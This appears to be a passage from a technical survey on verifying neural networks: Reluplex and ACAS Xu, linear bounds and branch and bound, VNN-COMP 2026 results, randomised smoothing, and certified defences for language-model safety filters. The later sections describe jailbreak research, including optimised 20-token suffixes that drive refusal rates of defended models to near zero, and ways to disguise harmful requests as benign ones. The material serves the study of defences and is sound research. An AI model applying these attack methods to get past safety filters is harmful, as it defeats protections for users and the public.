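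A layer can also be missing without anyone noticing. After discovering that its biology filters had been off for contractors' conversations, Anthropic ran Claude Sonnet 5 over everything people had typed during the affected period. According to Constantin, the model flagged 1,197 conversations as high risk, all but 62 from Anthropic's own teams or deliberate red-teaming. Staff read the 62 and found no clearly concerning misuse. The search would have missed any misuse that Sonnet 5 failed to detect, but it was far better than having no second layer.

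On 30 November 2026 Anthropic's chief executive, Dario Amodei, wrote in *We Must Pace the Frontier, Part 2* that the company had paused general release of new frontier models until its misuse filters improved. In June, by contrast, it had released Fable 5 behind a very broad filter and refined that filter while people used the model.

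## ACAS Xu and after: proving properties of whole networks

Testing cannot rule out worse failures than those already found, but a verifier can for some small networks. A verifier is a program that takes a network's weights and a precisely stated property and tries to prove that the property holds for every input in a given range. One of the first successes involved networks that help drones avoid collisions.

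ACAS Xu is a collision-avoidance system for unmanned aircraft. Its developers stored its advice in a lookup table of more than 2 GB, then explored replacing the table with 45 small neural networks that need less than 3 MB. *Reluplex* (Katz, Barrett and colleagues, 2017) describes a verifier of the same name and uses it to check the networks. Earlier certification work relied on 1.5 million simulated encounters. Even if none of those encounters ended in failure, the rule of three would still allow a failure rate of one in 500,000, and the result would cover only the kinds of encounter that the simulator produces.

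### What Reluplex proved

Each network receives five numbers: the distance ρ to the other aircraft in feet, the direction θ in which it lies, its heading ψ relative to the drone's own, and the two speeds. The network scores five possible pieces of advice: "clear of conflict" and a weak or strong turn to the left or right. The system issues the advice with the lowest score. The developers trained 45 networks, one for each combination of five previous pieces of advice and nine values of the time until the aircraft reach the same height.

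One property is that a network should never advise "clear of conflict" when another aircraft is straight ahead and approaching. In symbols, whenever

1500 ≤ ρ ≤ 1800, −0.06 ≤ θ ≤ 0.06, ψ ≥ 3.10, v_own ≥ 980 and v_int ≥ 960,

the score for "clear of conflict" is not the lowest of the five. Angles are in radians, so a ψ of at least 3.10 means that the two aircraft are flying almost directly at each other. Reluplex looks for an input that meets these conditions and breaks the conclusion. If it rules out every possibility, the property holds for all the infinitely many inputs in the range.

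The table shows five of the ten properties that Katz and colleagues tested.

| Property | Networks | Result | Total time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Aircraft ahead and approaching: never "clear of conflict" | 42 | Proved for all | 8 hours |
| Aircraft distant and much slower: score for "clear of conflict" stays below a limit | 45 | Proved for 41, out of time on 4 | 110 hours |
| Same situation: "clear of conflict" never has the worst score | 36 | Proved for 1, counterexamples for 35 | 23 hours |
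| Large vertical separation: never a strong turn | 1 | Out of time | – |
| Large vertical separation after "weak left": only "clear of conflict" or "weak left" | 1 | Counterexample | 11 hours |

The last counterexample was a real error, an input for which the network's output differed from the lookup table it was meant to replace. Simulations had already shown this kind of discrepancy, which Reluplex confirmed, and the developers planned to fix it by retraining.

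Katz and colleagues also checked robustness around five arbitrary inputs to one network. Around one of them, no change of up to 0.025 in the input values could alter the advice, but some change of up to 0.05 could. Proving robustness up to 0.1 around another took about four hours. They could prove robustness around every input at once only for much smaller networks.

### Bounding one small network by hand

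The networks use ReLUs, units that pass on positive numbers and replace negative ones with zero. The rest of each network only multiplies by fixed weights and adds. Once we specify which ReLUs pass on their input and which output zero, the network reduces to linear equations, which computers solve quickly. But with 300 ReLUs there are 2³⁰⁰ combinations, or about 2 × 10⁹⁰.

A network with one input and two ReLUs is enough to show how verifiers avoid checking every combination:

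y = ReLU(x) + ReLU(−x), with x between −1 and 1.

Suppose we want to prove that y never exceeds 1.5. The method that needs the least computation is interval arithmetic, which works out a range for each part separately. ReLU(x) and ReLU(−x) each lie between 0 and 1, so y lies between 0 and 2. This range is correct but too loose to prove the property, because the calculation doesn't use the fact that x and −x can't both be positive.

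Splitting the problem into two cases solves this. If x is at least 0, the second ReLU outputs 0 and y = x, which is at most 1. If x is at most 0, the first outputs 0 and y = −x, which is also at most 1. The two cases cover every input, so y ≤ 1 and the property holds.

Reluplex splits in this way but delays doing so. It extends the simplex method, a standard algorithm for linear inequalities, by treating the input and output of each ReLU as separate variables whose values may temporarily violate the ReLU function. It repairs these violations one at a time, and splits on a ReLU only after five attempts to repair it. Katz and colleagues often found that after splitting on about 10% of the ReLUs, the resulting bounds determined which case applied to each of the others.

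### Linear bounds, and branch and bound

Newer verifiers get more out of each calculation by using straight lines as bounds. If the input z to a ReLU lies between l and u, with l negative and u positive, then

ReLU(z) ≤ u(z − l)/(u − l).

The right-hand side is the line that joins the ReLU's values at the two ends of the range. In the example both ranges run from −1 to 1, so ReLU(x) ≤ (x + 1)/2 and ReLU(−x) ≤ (−x + 1)/2. Adding them gives

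y ≤ (x + 1)/2 + (−x + 1)/2 = 1.

The two x terms cancel, so the proof needs no splitting. CROWN, the method behind the leading verifier, carries lines like these through every layer of a network.

For the lower bound, we can use any line αz with α between 0 and 1, because they all stay below the ReLU. With a slope of 1 for the first ReLU and 0 for the second, we get only y ≥ x, and x can be as low as −1. With equal slopes we get y ≥ 0, which is exact. A later version called α-CROWN uses gradients to search for the best slopes, much as training searches for the best weights.

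Sometimes no choice of slopes is good enough. Take the function

t(x) = ReLU(x) − ReLU(2x − 1),

again with x between −1 and 1. Its graph is flat up to 0, rises to 0.5 at x = 0.5 and falls back to 0 at x = 1. The best upper bound that these lines can give is 0.75, so they can't prove that t(x) ≤ 0.6. If we split at x = 0, both ReLUs are zero on the left, and on the right the lines give exactly 0.5. One split is enough.

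Branch and bound combines the two techniques:

1. Compute bounds for the whole range of inputs. If they prove the property, stop.
2. Otherwise search for a counterexample, for instance with projected gradient descent. If there is one, stop.
3. Otherwise split the range, or one ReLU, into two cases and repeat the process on each.

Given enough time, this method can prove or disprove a property of any ReLU network, barring rounding errors. In practice the number of cases may grow exponentially, so success depends largely on choosing where to split.

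### Training networks that are easier to prove robust

The attacks used in adversarial training may miss the worst change to a photograph, so the loss they find is a lower limit on the true worst-case loss. Certified training uses bounds to calculate an upper limit, and adjusts the weights to reduce that instead:

min over θ of E[ U(θ, x, y) ], where U(θ, x, y) ≥ max over δ in S of L(θ, x + δ, y).

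Let U be an upper limit on a network's loss on a photograph under any permitted change. If U is small enough, no permitted change can alter the label the network gives the photograph. Trainers usually calculate U with interval arithmetic because it is fast, but the resulting limit is loose, and a network trained only to keep it small loses a lot of accuracy. A method called MTL-IBP therefore trains on a weighted average of U and the ordinary adversarial loss.

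VNN-COMP, an annual competition for neural network verifiers, included six networks trained this way in 2026. In *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)*, Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues (2026) report how many of 10,000 test images the verifier α,β-CROWN certified for each network, with a limit of 1,000 seconds per image. The last column adds the images on which the verifier ran out of time, since some of those may be robust too.

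| Images and permitted change | Network | Accuracy without attack | Certified accuracy | Out of time | Highest possible robust accuracy |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| CIFAR-10, 2/255 | Standard | 83.54% | 66.04% | 6.58% | 72.62% |
| CIFAR-10, 2/255 | Wide | 85.37% | 60.28% | 14.33% | 74.61% |
| CIFAR-10, 8/255 | Standard | 57.19% | 35.49% | 1.34% | 36.83% |
| CIFAR-10, 8/255 | Wide | 57.74% | 34.60% | 1.32% | 35.92% |
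| TinyImageNet, 1/255 | Standard | 41.21% | 27.81% | 2.36% | 30.17% |
| TinyImageNet, 1/255 | Wide | 41.89% | 28.35% | 4.01% | 32.36% |

At 2/255, the wide network has the lower certified accuracy of the two but may be more robust; the verifier timed out too often to tell. There is little uncertainty at 8/255, where the standard network's robust accuracy is between 35.49% and 36.83%, so a perfect verifier would raise its certified accuracy by at most 1.34 percentage points.

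The best adversarially trained network kept 74.97% accuracy under AutoAttack at the same 8/255, though that is an upper bound and the two networks differ in design and training data. The certified network also misclassifies more than four in ten unaltered photographs, which is a lot of accuracy to give up for a proof.

Of the 60,000 attempts, 2,994 (4.99%) ran out of time. At 1,000 seconds each, those attempts alone would take one machine almost 35 days. For larger image networks, researchers often use randomised smoothing, which gives a probabilistic certificate instead.

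### Why verification is hard

Verification is hard in the worst case because a small ReLU network can encode a logic puzzle called 3-SAT. In 3-SAT, we get a list of clauses such as "a or b or not c" and have to decide whether we can make each variable true or false so that every clause is satisfied. With 100 variables, there are about 10³⁰ combinations.

Katz and colleagues showed how to turn any such puzzle into a network. Let 1 stand for true and 0 for false, so that "not c" becomes 1 − c. The clause above becomes

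1 − ReLU(1 − (a + b + (1 − c))).

If all three parts are false, the sum inside is 0 and so is the result. If at least one is true, the sum is 1 or more, the ReLU outputs 0 and the result is 1. The network adds up the results for all n clauses, so its output reaches n only if every clause is true. A verifier that can decide whether the output ever reaches n can therefore solve the puzzle.

The inputs also have to be exactly 0 or 1, although a network accepts anything in between. The function t(x) from the branch-and-bound example takes care of this, because between 0 and 1 it equals zero only at the two ends, so the property can require it to be zero for every variable. (The gadget that Katz and colleagues printed for this purpose contains a slip, since it also lets through an input of 0.5.)

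Finding an input that violates a property is therefore NP-complete, which means that a method that solved every case quickly could also be used to quickly solve every other problem whose solutions are easy to check. *Complexity of Injectivity and Verification of ReLU Neural Networks* (2024) proves that verification remains hard even for networks with a single hidden layer and a single output.

Having few inputs does help. A ReLU network divides its input space into regions and is linear within each one, so a verifier could check the regions one by one. In *Parameterized Hardness of Zonotope Containment and Neural Network Verification*, Froese, Grillo and colleagues (2025) give the running time as roughly n^((ℓ−1)d), for d inputs, ℓ layers and at most n units in each hidden layer. For an ACAS Xu network, with five inputs and six hidden layers of 50 units, that is 50³⁰, or about 10⁵¹ steps.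 This is far fewer than 2³⁰⁰ but still too many to carry out.

### What the refutation of the Exponential Time Hypothesis changed

Froese and colleagues also argued that going through the regions is essentially the best possible method in the worst case. Their argument assumed the Exponential Time Hypothesis. As *Running-Time Lower Bounds under FPT ≠ W[1]* (2026) states it, the hypothesis says that for some constant c > 0, no algorithm solves every 3-SAT puzzle with n variables in 2^(cn) steps, apart from a factor that grows much more slowly. In October 2026 OpenAI and Anthropic each published an algorithm that refutes it. The new algorithms take

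2^(O(n log log n / √log n))

steps, so the exponent grows slightly more slowly than n.

The claim that no method is faster than enumeration has therefore lost its support, even if no one has found a faster method. The proofs that verification is NP-complete still stand because they never relied on the hypothesis. Froese and colleagues' proofs of W-hardness also stand, and they give a different reason to doubt that verification is easy when a network has few inputs.

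In *ETH is Dead, Long Live SH*, Brunner, Demaine and colleagues (2026) show that many of the lower bounds based on the hypothesis still hold, with slightly smaller exponents, under a weaker conjecture from 1990. This conjecture rules out only algorithms whose exponent is at most n^(1−ε) for some fixed ε > 0.

Verifiers don't get any faster either. In *Lowered crossover points of Anthropic's subexponential 3-SAT algorithm*, Majdoddin (2026) calculated how large a problem must be before Anthropic's algorithm overtakes the best older ones. Even after improvements, and for a favourable type of problem, it must have about 2⁴²⁰ (10¹²⁶) clauses, far more than the number of atoms in the observable universe.

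Translating a network into 3-SAT could also cancel the gain. *Monotone Local Search with Sample-Dependent Running Times* (2026) points out that for some graph problems the natural translation multiplies the number of variables by about log n, which is enough to lose the advantage. A network's weights and activations are numbers with many binary digits, so encoding its arithmetic as true-or-false clauses would take many variables per unit.

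### The 2026 competition

VNN-COMP runs all the verifiers on rented machines of equal cost. In 2026 its main track had 3,373 problems in 24 sets worth up to 100 points each. α,β-CROWN came first with 2,344.0 points. It had also won the previous year's contest, which Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues describe in *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)* (2025).

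Vibecheck came second, with 2,278.6 points. Doug Wehbe and Stanley Bak of Stony Brook University had Anthropic's Claude Code write it in two months, mostly with the Claude Opus 4.8 model. It solved 3,108 problems, against 3,164 for α,β-CROWN, a tool that several universities have developed over years. AI can evidently reproduce most of the state of the art in this field with little effort, although Vibecheck largely combines techniques people had already published.

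Another entry, SuperSimple, shows how much of the difficulty lies in proving things. It runs a standard attack and then computes linear bounds, but never splits. It found 1,007 counterexamples, compared with α,β-CROWN's 1,182, but only 544 proofs compared with 1,982. (It also ran without a graphics chip and took part in fewer problem sets, so splitting may not account for the whole difference.)

The largest network, an image classifier called VGG-16, has 138 million weights. In the 18 problems set for it, the part of the image that may change ranges from one randomly chosen pixel to all 150,528 input values. A proof about one pixel of one photograph is much easier than the size of the network suggests, and it covers almost none of what an attacker could do.

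The vision transformers in the competition have only 68,000 to 76,000 weights. Their designers kept them shallow and narrow so that verifiers might be able to handle them, and replaced one standard component with another. The networks label about 60% of CIFAR-10 photographs correctly, and the permitted change is only 1/255. The problem set excludes photographs that an attack could cause a network to mislabel and those that a basic method could easily verify, leaving the harder cases.

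Even Llama-3.1-8B has about 100,000 times as many weights as these transformers. Better hardware alone is unlikely to close that gap, because the number of cases to check can grow exponentially with the number of units. A proof about a chatbot's whole reply would also have to cover hundreds of runs of the network, one for each token.

### When the verifier is wrong

A verification tool's proof can be wrong if the tool has a bug. VNN-COMP gives 10 points for a correct answer and deducts 150 for a wrong one, so guessing raises a tool's expected score only if it is right more than 93.75% of the time. Several tools still gave wrong answers. Ladner and colleagues count results that were incorrect or whose counterexamples were missing from the output: 94 for NeuralSAT, 58 for nnenum and one for α,β-CROWN. Agate had 955, in part because a last-minute bug corrupted the counterexamples it reported.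 They list none for Vibecheck.

These counts leave out mistakes that nobody caught. The organisers usually don't know the right answer in advance, so they rely on one tool finding a counterexample to a property that another claims to have proved. If every tool wrongly declares a property proved, they all score points. Two of the problem sets address this. One contains hidden counterexamples that ordinary attacks have trouble finding, and the other uses the construction described above to turn 100 logic puzzles with known answers into networks.

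Rounding is a subtler source of error. Most verifiers are designed for exact real numbers, but computers round after every operation. The Reluplex method is mathematically sound, but Katz and colleagues admitted that their implementation used rounded arithmetic for speed and so did not guarantee soundness, although it checked the accumulated error.

A proof that is correct for real numbers may not hold for the software that runs, because software rounds its calculations. In *Floating-Point Neural Network Verification at the Software Level*, Manino, Farias and colleagues (2025) give the example of the function x/(|x| + 1), which should never fall as x rises. In 32-bit floating-point arithmetic, an input of 15 gives 0.9375, but an input of about 15.000003 gives about 0.93749994. They cite work showing that such discrepancies are large enough to invalidate many of the proofs verifiers produce.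 An attacker who knows how a system rounds could look for inputs that exploit these discrepancies.

One remedy is to verify the program code instead of the idealised network. Manino and colleagues tested eight general software verifiers on 912 pieces of neural network code. On average, the tools were right on 11%, wrong on 3% and reached no verdict on the rest, which makes them much too unreliable for certification.

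Rounding has also been a problem in VNN-COMP. In earlier years the organisers accepted counterexamples that narrowly missed the stated limits, so one tool could prove a property, another could "refute" it, and both could count as correct. Since 2026 the input has to meet the limits exactly. If the output misses by no more than 0.0001, the tool that found the counterexample keeps its points, but the organisers don't use that result against a tool that reports a proof.

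A better solution is for verifiers to write out their proofs. Anyone can check a counterexample by running the network on it, but users usually have to trust a verifier's claim that none exists. A branch-and-bound verifier could list every split it made and the bounds that settle each case. A much smaller program could then check the list with exact arithmetic, and users would have to trust only that program. Katz and colleagues suggested this in 2017, and Ladner and colleagues name it as a long-term goal for the competition. Checking proofs this way would catch bugs in the verifier, but the proof would still apply only to the idealised network unless it also accounted for rounding.

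### Writing down what should be proved

Programmers normally know what each part of their code is supposed to do. *Neural Network Verification is a Programming Language Challenge* (2025) notes that people commonly see neural networks as programs that emerge from data, without anyone directing how they compute. Someone therefore has to write the specification separately, and it may be wrong.

For example, one ACAS Xu property required that "clear of conflict" never get the worst score when the other aircraft is far away and much slower. Reluplex found counterexamples in 35 of the 36 networks, but the researchers decided that the behaviour was acceptable because the networks strongly favour repeating their previous advice, so the mistake was in the property. Even together, the ten properties don't directly address collisions. Proving that drones following the advice stay apart would also require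 a model of how aircraft move, which Katz and colleagues left for later work.

The developers of ACAS Xu could define bad advice in terms of distances, angles and speeds. Electrical engineers can likewise define a bad plan for operating a power grid. In one set of problems in VNN-COMP 2026, the task is to check whether a network's plans for a grid can break the limits on voltage, generation or the load on each line by more than a set amount.

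Nobody can yet do this for "the chatbot never gives a harmful answer". The closest attempt in the competition is safeNLP, which covers questions about whether the user is talking to a robot, and requests for medical advice. Its designers took a sentence, generated many rewordings, and used a language model to turn each into a list of 30 numbers. They treated each list as a point and computed the smallest box that contains all the points. The verifier then tries to prove that a small classifier gives every point in the box the same label.

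A successful proof covers infinitely many points, including those for rewordings that nobody wrote. But some rewordings may fall outside the box, and some points inside it may correspond to no sentence, or to one with a different meaning. The proof also doesn't cover the language model that produced the numbers. The classifier has about 4,000 weights and only recognises a type of question, so the proof doesn't show that the chatbot then answers it safely.

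### Guaranteed Safe AI

Some researchers want to extend this approach to much more powerful systems. In *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (2024), David Dalrymple, Joar Skalse and colleagues describe a family of methods with three parts. A world model describes mathematically how the system's actions affect the world, and a safety specification states which effects are acceptable. A verifier produces a proof, which anyone can audit, that the system meets the specification if the world model is right.

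For a drone, the world model would contain the equations of flight, and the specification might be a minimum distance from other aircraft. The verifier's proof would then cover collisions, which the ten ACAS Xu properties did not.

Andrew Dickson objected in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024) that proofs are about symbols, and that we lack models of biology, people or societies accurate enough for a proof to establish much about the real world. A version of this problem arises even with simple machines. One VNN-COMP problem set, on the stability of a small drone's controller, uses a neural network trained to approximate the drone's motion. A proof would therefore apply to the approximation, and the real drone might behave differently.

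Dalrymple and colleagues accept that any guarantee depends on the world model, but they answer that the model can include its own uncertainty. The verifier would then prove an upper limit on the probability of harm. This works if the stated uncertainty is wide enough to include what happens. For a drone in gusty wind, engineers can measure how much the wind varies. Nobody knows how to choose the range for the effects of advice given to millions of people, and a range wide enough to be safe may produce a limit too high to be useful.

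The British government's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) set up a £59 million programme called Safeguarded AI to develop the idea, with Dalrymple as its director. Under the original plan, advanced AI would help experts write world models and specifications, then produce controllers for particular tasks together with proofs about them. If events departed from the world model during use, a simpler backup controller would take over. The plan started with areas such as energy networks and supply chains, where failure is easier to define in numbers.

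## Randomised smoothing: a certificate obtained by voting

Randomised smoothing avoids the size limits of exact verification by treating the network as a black box. The method makes many copies of a photograph, adds different random noise to each, has the network label them, and gives the majority label as its answer. If the majority is large enough, no change to the photograph below a certain size can change the answer.

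In *Certified Adversarial Robustness via Randomized Smoothing* (2019), Cohen, Rosenfeld and Kolter proved the strongest guarantee that a vote under Gaussian noise allows. They applied it to ImageNet, a set of photographs in 1,000 classes, where no other kind of certificate worked at full resolution. The guarantee covers the whole procedure of adding noise and voting, but the network on its own is as easy to fool as before.

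### From a majority to a distance

Gaussian noise changes every colour value by an independent random amount drawn from a bell curve with standard deviation σ. Colour values here run from 0 to 1, so σ = 0.5 gives a very grainy picture. Let p be the probability that the network labels a noisy copy of photograph x "cat", and suppose for simplicity that the only other label is "dog". The attacker adds a change δ to x. Its size r is the square root of the sum of the squared changes to the colour values.

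The noisy copies form a cloud around x, and the attack moves the centre of the cloud to x + δ. The old and new clouds overlap, so many noisy pictures could have come from either. For a noisy picture z, the likelihood ratio compares how probable it is after the attack with how probable it was before:

exp( δ·(z − x)/σ² − r²/(2σ²) ).

The term δ·(z − x) measures how far z lies from x in the attacker's direction. The ratio increases with this term and depends on z only through it.

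All we know about the network is that it says "cat" on a fraction p of the copies before the attack, so we have to assume the worst network that fits this fact. That network would say "cat" on the pictures that the attack makes rarest, which are those with the lowest ratios. The distance then follows in four steps:

1. The lowest ratios lie on the side away from the attack. The worst network therefore says "cat" up to some cut-off t in the attacker's direction and "dog" beyond it.
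2. Before the attack, positions along this direction follow a bell curve centred on 0 with standard deviation σ. A fraction p lies below the cut-off, so t = σΦ⁻¹(p). Here Φ(s) is the fraction of a bell curve that lies below s standard deviations, and Φ⁻¹ reverses the calculation.
3. The attack moves the centre of the curve to r, which leaves "cat" with a share of Φ(Φ⁻¹(p) − r/σ).
4. This share stays above one half as long as r is smaller than

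R = σΦ⁻¹(p).

With σ = 0.5 and p = 0.9, Φ⁻¹(p) is 1.28 and R is 0.64. An attack of size 0.3 could cut the share of "cat" votes from 90% to 75% at worst, and only an attack of at least 0.64 could reduce it to 50%. Nobody can prove a larger R from p alone, because for any larger change, some possible network with the same p would switch its majority label.

### Why more votes help so little

Nobody can calculate p exactly for a real network, so Cohen and colleagues estimated it. They used 100 noisy copies to guess the winning label and another 100,000 to find a lower limit on p with 99.9% confidence. If the network labels 90,000 of those 100,000 copies "cat", the lower limit is about 0.897 and R drops slightly to 0.63.

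Even a unanimous vote leaves some doubt about p. As in the rule of three, but at 99.9% confidence, the lower limit on p after n unanimous votes solves pⁿ = 0.001. For n = 100,000 this gives p = 0.99993, so R is at most 3.8σ, even for a network that gives every possible picture the same label. A million votes would raise the maximum R only to about 4.4σ, and a thousand would still allow 2.5σ. Consistent with this, Seferis, Wu and colleagues (2025) found in *Randomized Smoothing Meets Vision-Language Models* that a hundred to a thousand times fewer samples can be enough with little loss.

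Cohen and colleagues took 110 seconds to certify one ImageNet photograph. Taking a vote of 100 copies without computing a distance took 0.15 seconds, but the vote was too close on 12% of photographs, so the system gave no answer for them. With 10,000 copies, this fell to 1%. An attacker who can't change the answer may still be able to make the vote so close that the system gives no answer.

### A small distance in a large image

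An ImageNet photograph usually has 224 by 224 pixels with three colour values each, or 150,528 numbers. An attacker with a budget of 0.64 could spend it all on one number and change it by 163 of the 255 steps. Spread evenly over all the numbers, the same budget allows a change of

0.64/√150,528 ≈ 0.0017,

or about 0.4/255, which is less than half of the smallest step that an ordinary image file can record. The certificate therefore doesn't cover a change of one step to every number.

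The usual CIFAR-10 limit of 8/255 per number allows a change with an overall size of about 12.2 on an ImageNet photograph. Since 100,000 votes certify at most 3.8σ, certifying a change that large would require a σ of at least 3.2. That is more than three times the whole range from black to white, and no classifier could recognise much through so much noise.

Other kinds of noise don't solve the problem. *Curse of Dimensionality on Randomized Smoothing for Certifiable Robustness* (Kumar, Levine and colleagues, 2020) proves that, for a wide class of noise distributions, the largest change we can certify to every number in an image at once shrinks in proportion to 1/√d, where d is how many numbers the image has. Within a broad family of bell-shaped distributions, none beats Gaussian noise by more than a constant factor. *Randomized Smoothing of All Shapes and Sizes* (2020) proves a similar limit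 for every smoothing method that uses only the share of votes. A method that used more information from the network could escape this limit, but one such algorithm takes 100 times as long.

Cohen and colleagues had argued that larger images also tolerate more noise. If we enlarge a photograph from 56 to 224 pixels across, each original pixel becomes 16 pixels, and averaging those 16 cuts the noise to a quarter. We can therefore use four times as much noise and certify four times the distance. But √d is also four times as large, so at best the guarantee for each number stays the same.

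### Adding a denoiser

The certificate is only useful if the network can still recognise objects through the noise. Cohen and colleagues trained their network on noisy photographs. In *(Certified!!) Adversarial Robustness for Free!*, Carlini, Tramèr and colleagues (2022) used a publicly available diffusion model to remove the noise and passed the result to an ordinary classifier, without retraining either. The proof holds for any function, so it applies unchanged to the diffusion model and classifier combined.

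The table gives the share of ImageNet test photographs that each method labelled correctly and certified, from the comparison by Carlini and colleagues.

| Overall size of change | Cohen and colleagues, 2019 | Best other method without a diffusion model | With a diffusion model, 2022 |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.5 | 49% | 57.0% | 71.1% |
| 1.0 | 37% | 44.6% | 54.3% |
| 1.5 | 29% | 39.8% | 38.1% |
| 2.0 | 19% | 30.4% | 29.5% |
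| 3.0 | 12% | 23.4% | 13.1% |

The denoiser helped a lot with small changes but not at all with large ones. The number of votes may be part of the reason. Carlini and colleagues used 10,000 noisy copies of each photograph, and with σ = 1, a certificate for a change of size 3.0 allows at most three votes against the winning label.

Later researchers worked on the denoiser's mistakes and on the choice of noise. *Robustifying Diffusion-Denoised Smoothing Against Covariate Shift* (Hedayatnia, Tavassolipour and colleagues, 2025) searched for noise that the diffusion model removes badly and trained the classifier on the results, which raised certified accuracy on both CIFAR-10 and ImageNet. *Dual Randomized Smoothing* (Sun et al., 2026) chose the noise level separately for each photograph and reported advantages on ImageNet of 8.6%, 17.1% and 9.1% at attack sizes 0.5, 1.0 and 1.5. The proof assumes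 the same noise before and after the attack, so the chosen level must be the same for the original photograph and the attacked one. These gains are useful but far too small to overcome the dimension problem.

### Changed tokens instead of changed pixels

Certified defences for language models usually limit how many tokens the attacker may add or replace.

Erase-and-check, which Aounon Kumar and others proposed in 2023, defends against attacks that add tokens to a harmful request. Suppose an attacker may append up to 20 tokens. The defence erases the last token, then the last two, and so on up to 20. A filter checks the full prompt and each shortened version, and the defence blocks the prompt if the filter flags any of them. One of these versions is the original request, so if the filter flags that request, the defence will also block it with up to 20 tokens appended. This guarantee needs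 no voting, but it takes 21 checks, and each extra check adds a chance of a false alarm. If the attacker may insert up to three tokens anywhere in what becomes a 30-token prompt, there are 4,526 versions to check. The guarantee also doesn't cover attacks that reword the request itself.

Token-level smoothing covers replaced tokens. The defence makes many copies of a prompt, randomly masks some tokens in each or swaps them for others, and has a detector judge whether each copy is harmful. Chen, Wei and colleagues (2025), in *Towards the Worst-case Robustness of Large Language Models*, work out what this guarantees. Suppose the noise masks each token with probability β and the attacker has replaced d tokens. With probability βᵈ the noise masks all d of them, and the detector then sees exactly what it would have seen without the attack. If we assume that the attacker wins in every other case,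 the share of "harmful" verdicts falls from p to no less than

p − (1 − βᵈ).

With β = 0.1 and two replaced tokens, βᵈ is 0.01. Even if the detector recognised every copy of the original request, the formula would guarantee only 1% of the votes after the attack. A majority vote would certify nothing, so this kind of defence has to block a prompt even when only a small minority of votes flag it.

### Attacks and certificates on the same defences

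Chen and colleagues first attacked the defences. They took 50 harmful requests and searched for 20 tokens to append to each. Four of the defences involved no randomness: a filter for unnatural text and three ways of adding safety instructions or examples to the prompt. When they searched against the undefended model and tried the tokens on the defended one, the three models still refused 70% to 100% of the requests. When they searched against the complete defended system, refusals fell to 0% in eleven of the twelve combinations of model and defence and to 2% in the other. They counted refusals by looking for stock phrases, which is an unreliable measure, but the gap is too large for that to explain it.

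The same attack left three defences that use random noise with refusal rates between 62% and 88%. Chen and colleagues don't take these figures as evidence of robustness, because the randomness may only have made successful attacks hard to find. Such attacks very probably exist, since twenty tokens are enough to make a harmful request look like a request for a safety warning. The researchers therefore also computed certificates to get a lower bound.

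With random token swaps, a detector built on GPT-4o had an average certified radius of 2.02 tokens, so on average an attacker could replace about two tokens anywhere in the request without getting it past the detector. A second setup left the first ten tokens of each prompt untouched, added padding at the end, and applied noise to everything after the tenth token. A detector built on Llama-3-8B then had an average radius of 6.41 tokens. That figure counts replacements within the padded region, so it doesn't mean the detector withstands any six-token suffix. Neither certificate covers inserted or deleted tokens.

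Both figures depend on a very low threshold. The defence blocks a prompt if more than 0.0046% of its noisy copies look harmful. Chen and colleagues chose this threshold using harmless prompts from a standard benchmark, but did not separately measure how often the defence blocks harmless prompts in general use. When they raised the threshold to 10%, the average radius in the first setting fell to zero.

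The threshold also makes the guarantee expensive to use. A successful certificate may guarantee only that 46 in a million copies of the attacked prompt will look harmful. By the rule of three, a service would need about 65,000 copies of a prompt to have a 95% chance of finding at least one that looks harmful. Chen and colleagues used a million copies per prompt to compute the certificates. Few companies would pay to check so many copies of every message, when trained filters such as Anthropic's add only a small percentage to the cost of a reply.

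Adding more noise can make the radius as large as one likes. In the second setting, raising the probability of changing each token from 0.25 to 0.5 increased the average radius from 6.41 to 11.47. At a probability of 1, the radius is infinite because the detector receives no information about the text after the first ten tokens. An attacker can then write anything there without affecting the verdict, including words that change what the request means.

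### Newer methods for text

Researchers have since tried to make the perturbation set more realistic. *Certifying Robustness Large Language Models via Discrete-Continuous Randomized Smoothing* (2026) counts the changed tokens and also measures how far each one moves in the model's embedding space, so replacing a word with a close synonym can count as a smaller change than replacing it with an unrelated word. The method handles appended text by adding dummy tokens that the attacker may replace, so it covers suffixes of a fixed length. *Certified Robustness under Heterogeneous Perturbations via Hybrid Randomized Smoothing* (Delattre, Wu and colleagues, 2026) certifies filters for prompts that combine an image with text, with a separate limit on changes to each. Such filters have to assess the two together, since a harmless picture and a harmless sentence can make a harmful request.

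*CluCERT* (Wang, Jin and colleagues, 2025) uses synonyms as the noise. A language model first cuts the text down to its most informative words. The method then groups the noisy copies by meaning and counts only the votes of the largest group, which tends to increase the majority and therefore the radius. But the radius counts changes to the shortened text, and an attacker who edits the full text might affect which words are kept. The formula also scales down the effect of an attack by a stability factor between 0 and 1. If this factor is too low for even one permitted change, the certificate may be wrong.

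Cheng, Yang and colleagues (2026) report a much larger radius in *Provable Defense Framework for LLM Jailbreaks via Noise-Augumented Alignment*, but their proof doesn't support it. They keep a random sample of the prompt's tokens, hide the others, and take a majority vote on whether to refuse. They also fine-tune the model on incomplete prompts, which models otherwise handle badly. With 70% of the tokens kept, they report an average radius of 14.6 tokens against attacks that add optimised text.

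Let ρ be the probability that the sample contains none of the attacker's tokens. The proof shows that the verdict is safe if the two sides' shares of the vote differ by more than 2(1 − ρ), but the theorem gives the condition as 1 − 2ρ. With 70% of the tokens kept, ρ is 0.3 for a single altered token, so the shares would have to differ by more than 1.4. They can't differ by more than 1, so the method certifies nothing at this setting. With 10% kept, the method can certify against up to six altered tokens under the correct condition, but the model's MMLU score falls from 67.9% to 34.2%.

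Cheng and colleagues also found that the success rate of these attacks fell from 84.2% to 1.2%. This result doesn't depend on the theorem, but random noise may have obstructed their attack, as it obstructed Chen and colleagues'.

### A stable verdict can still be wrong

A certificate establishes that nearby inputs get the same answer, but that answer may be wrong. If a network labels 99% of the noisy copies of one cat photograph "toaster" and 90% of the noisy copies of another "cat", the certified distance is larger for the first. Researchers can exclude such mistakes from certified accuracy because they know the correct labels of the test photographs. Someone who receives a photograph in practice learns only that if an attacker changed it by less than R, the original would have got the same label.

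For text, the number of tokens replaced is also a poor measure of how much a request has changed. A certificate for two or six tokens doesn't cover a translation, which replaces nearly every token but keeps the meaning. Replacing a few well-chosen tokens, however, can make the same request harmless. Chen and colleagues examined their 50 requests and estimated that, on average, an attacker could replace only 2.12 tokens before the request might stop being harmful. The GPT-4o detector's radius of 2.02 is close to that figure. A much larger radius would make the detector flag requests that had become harmless.

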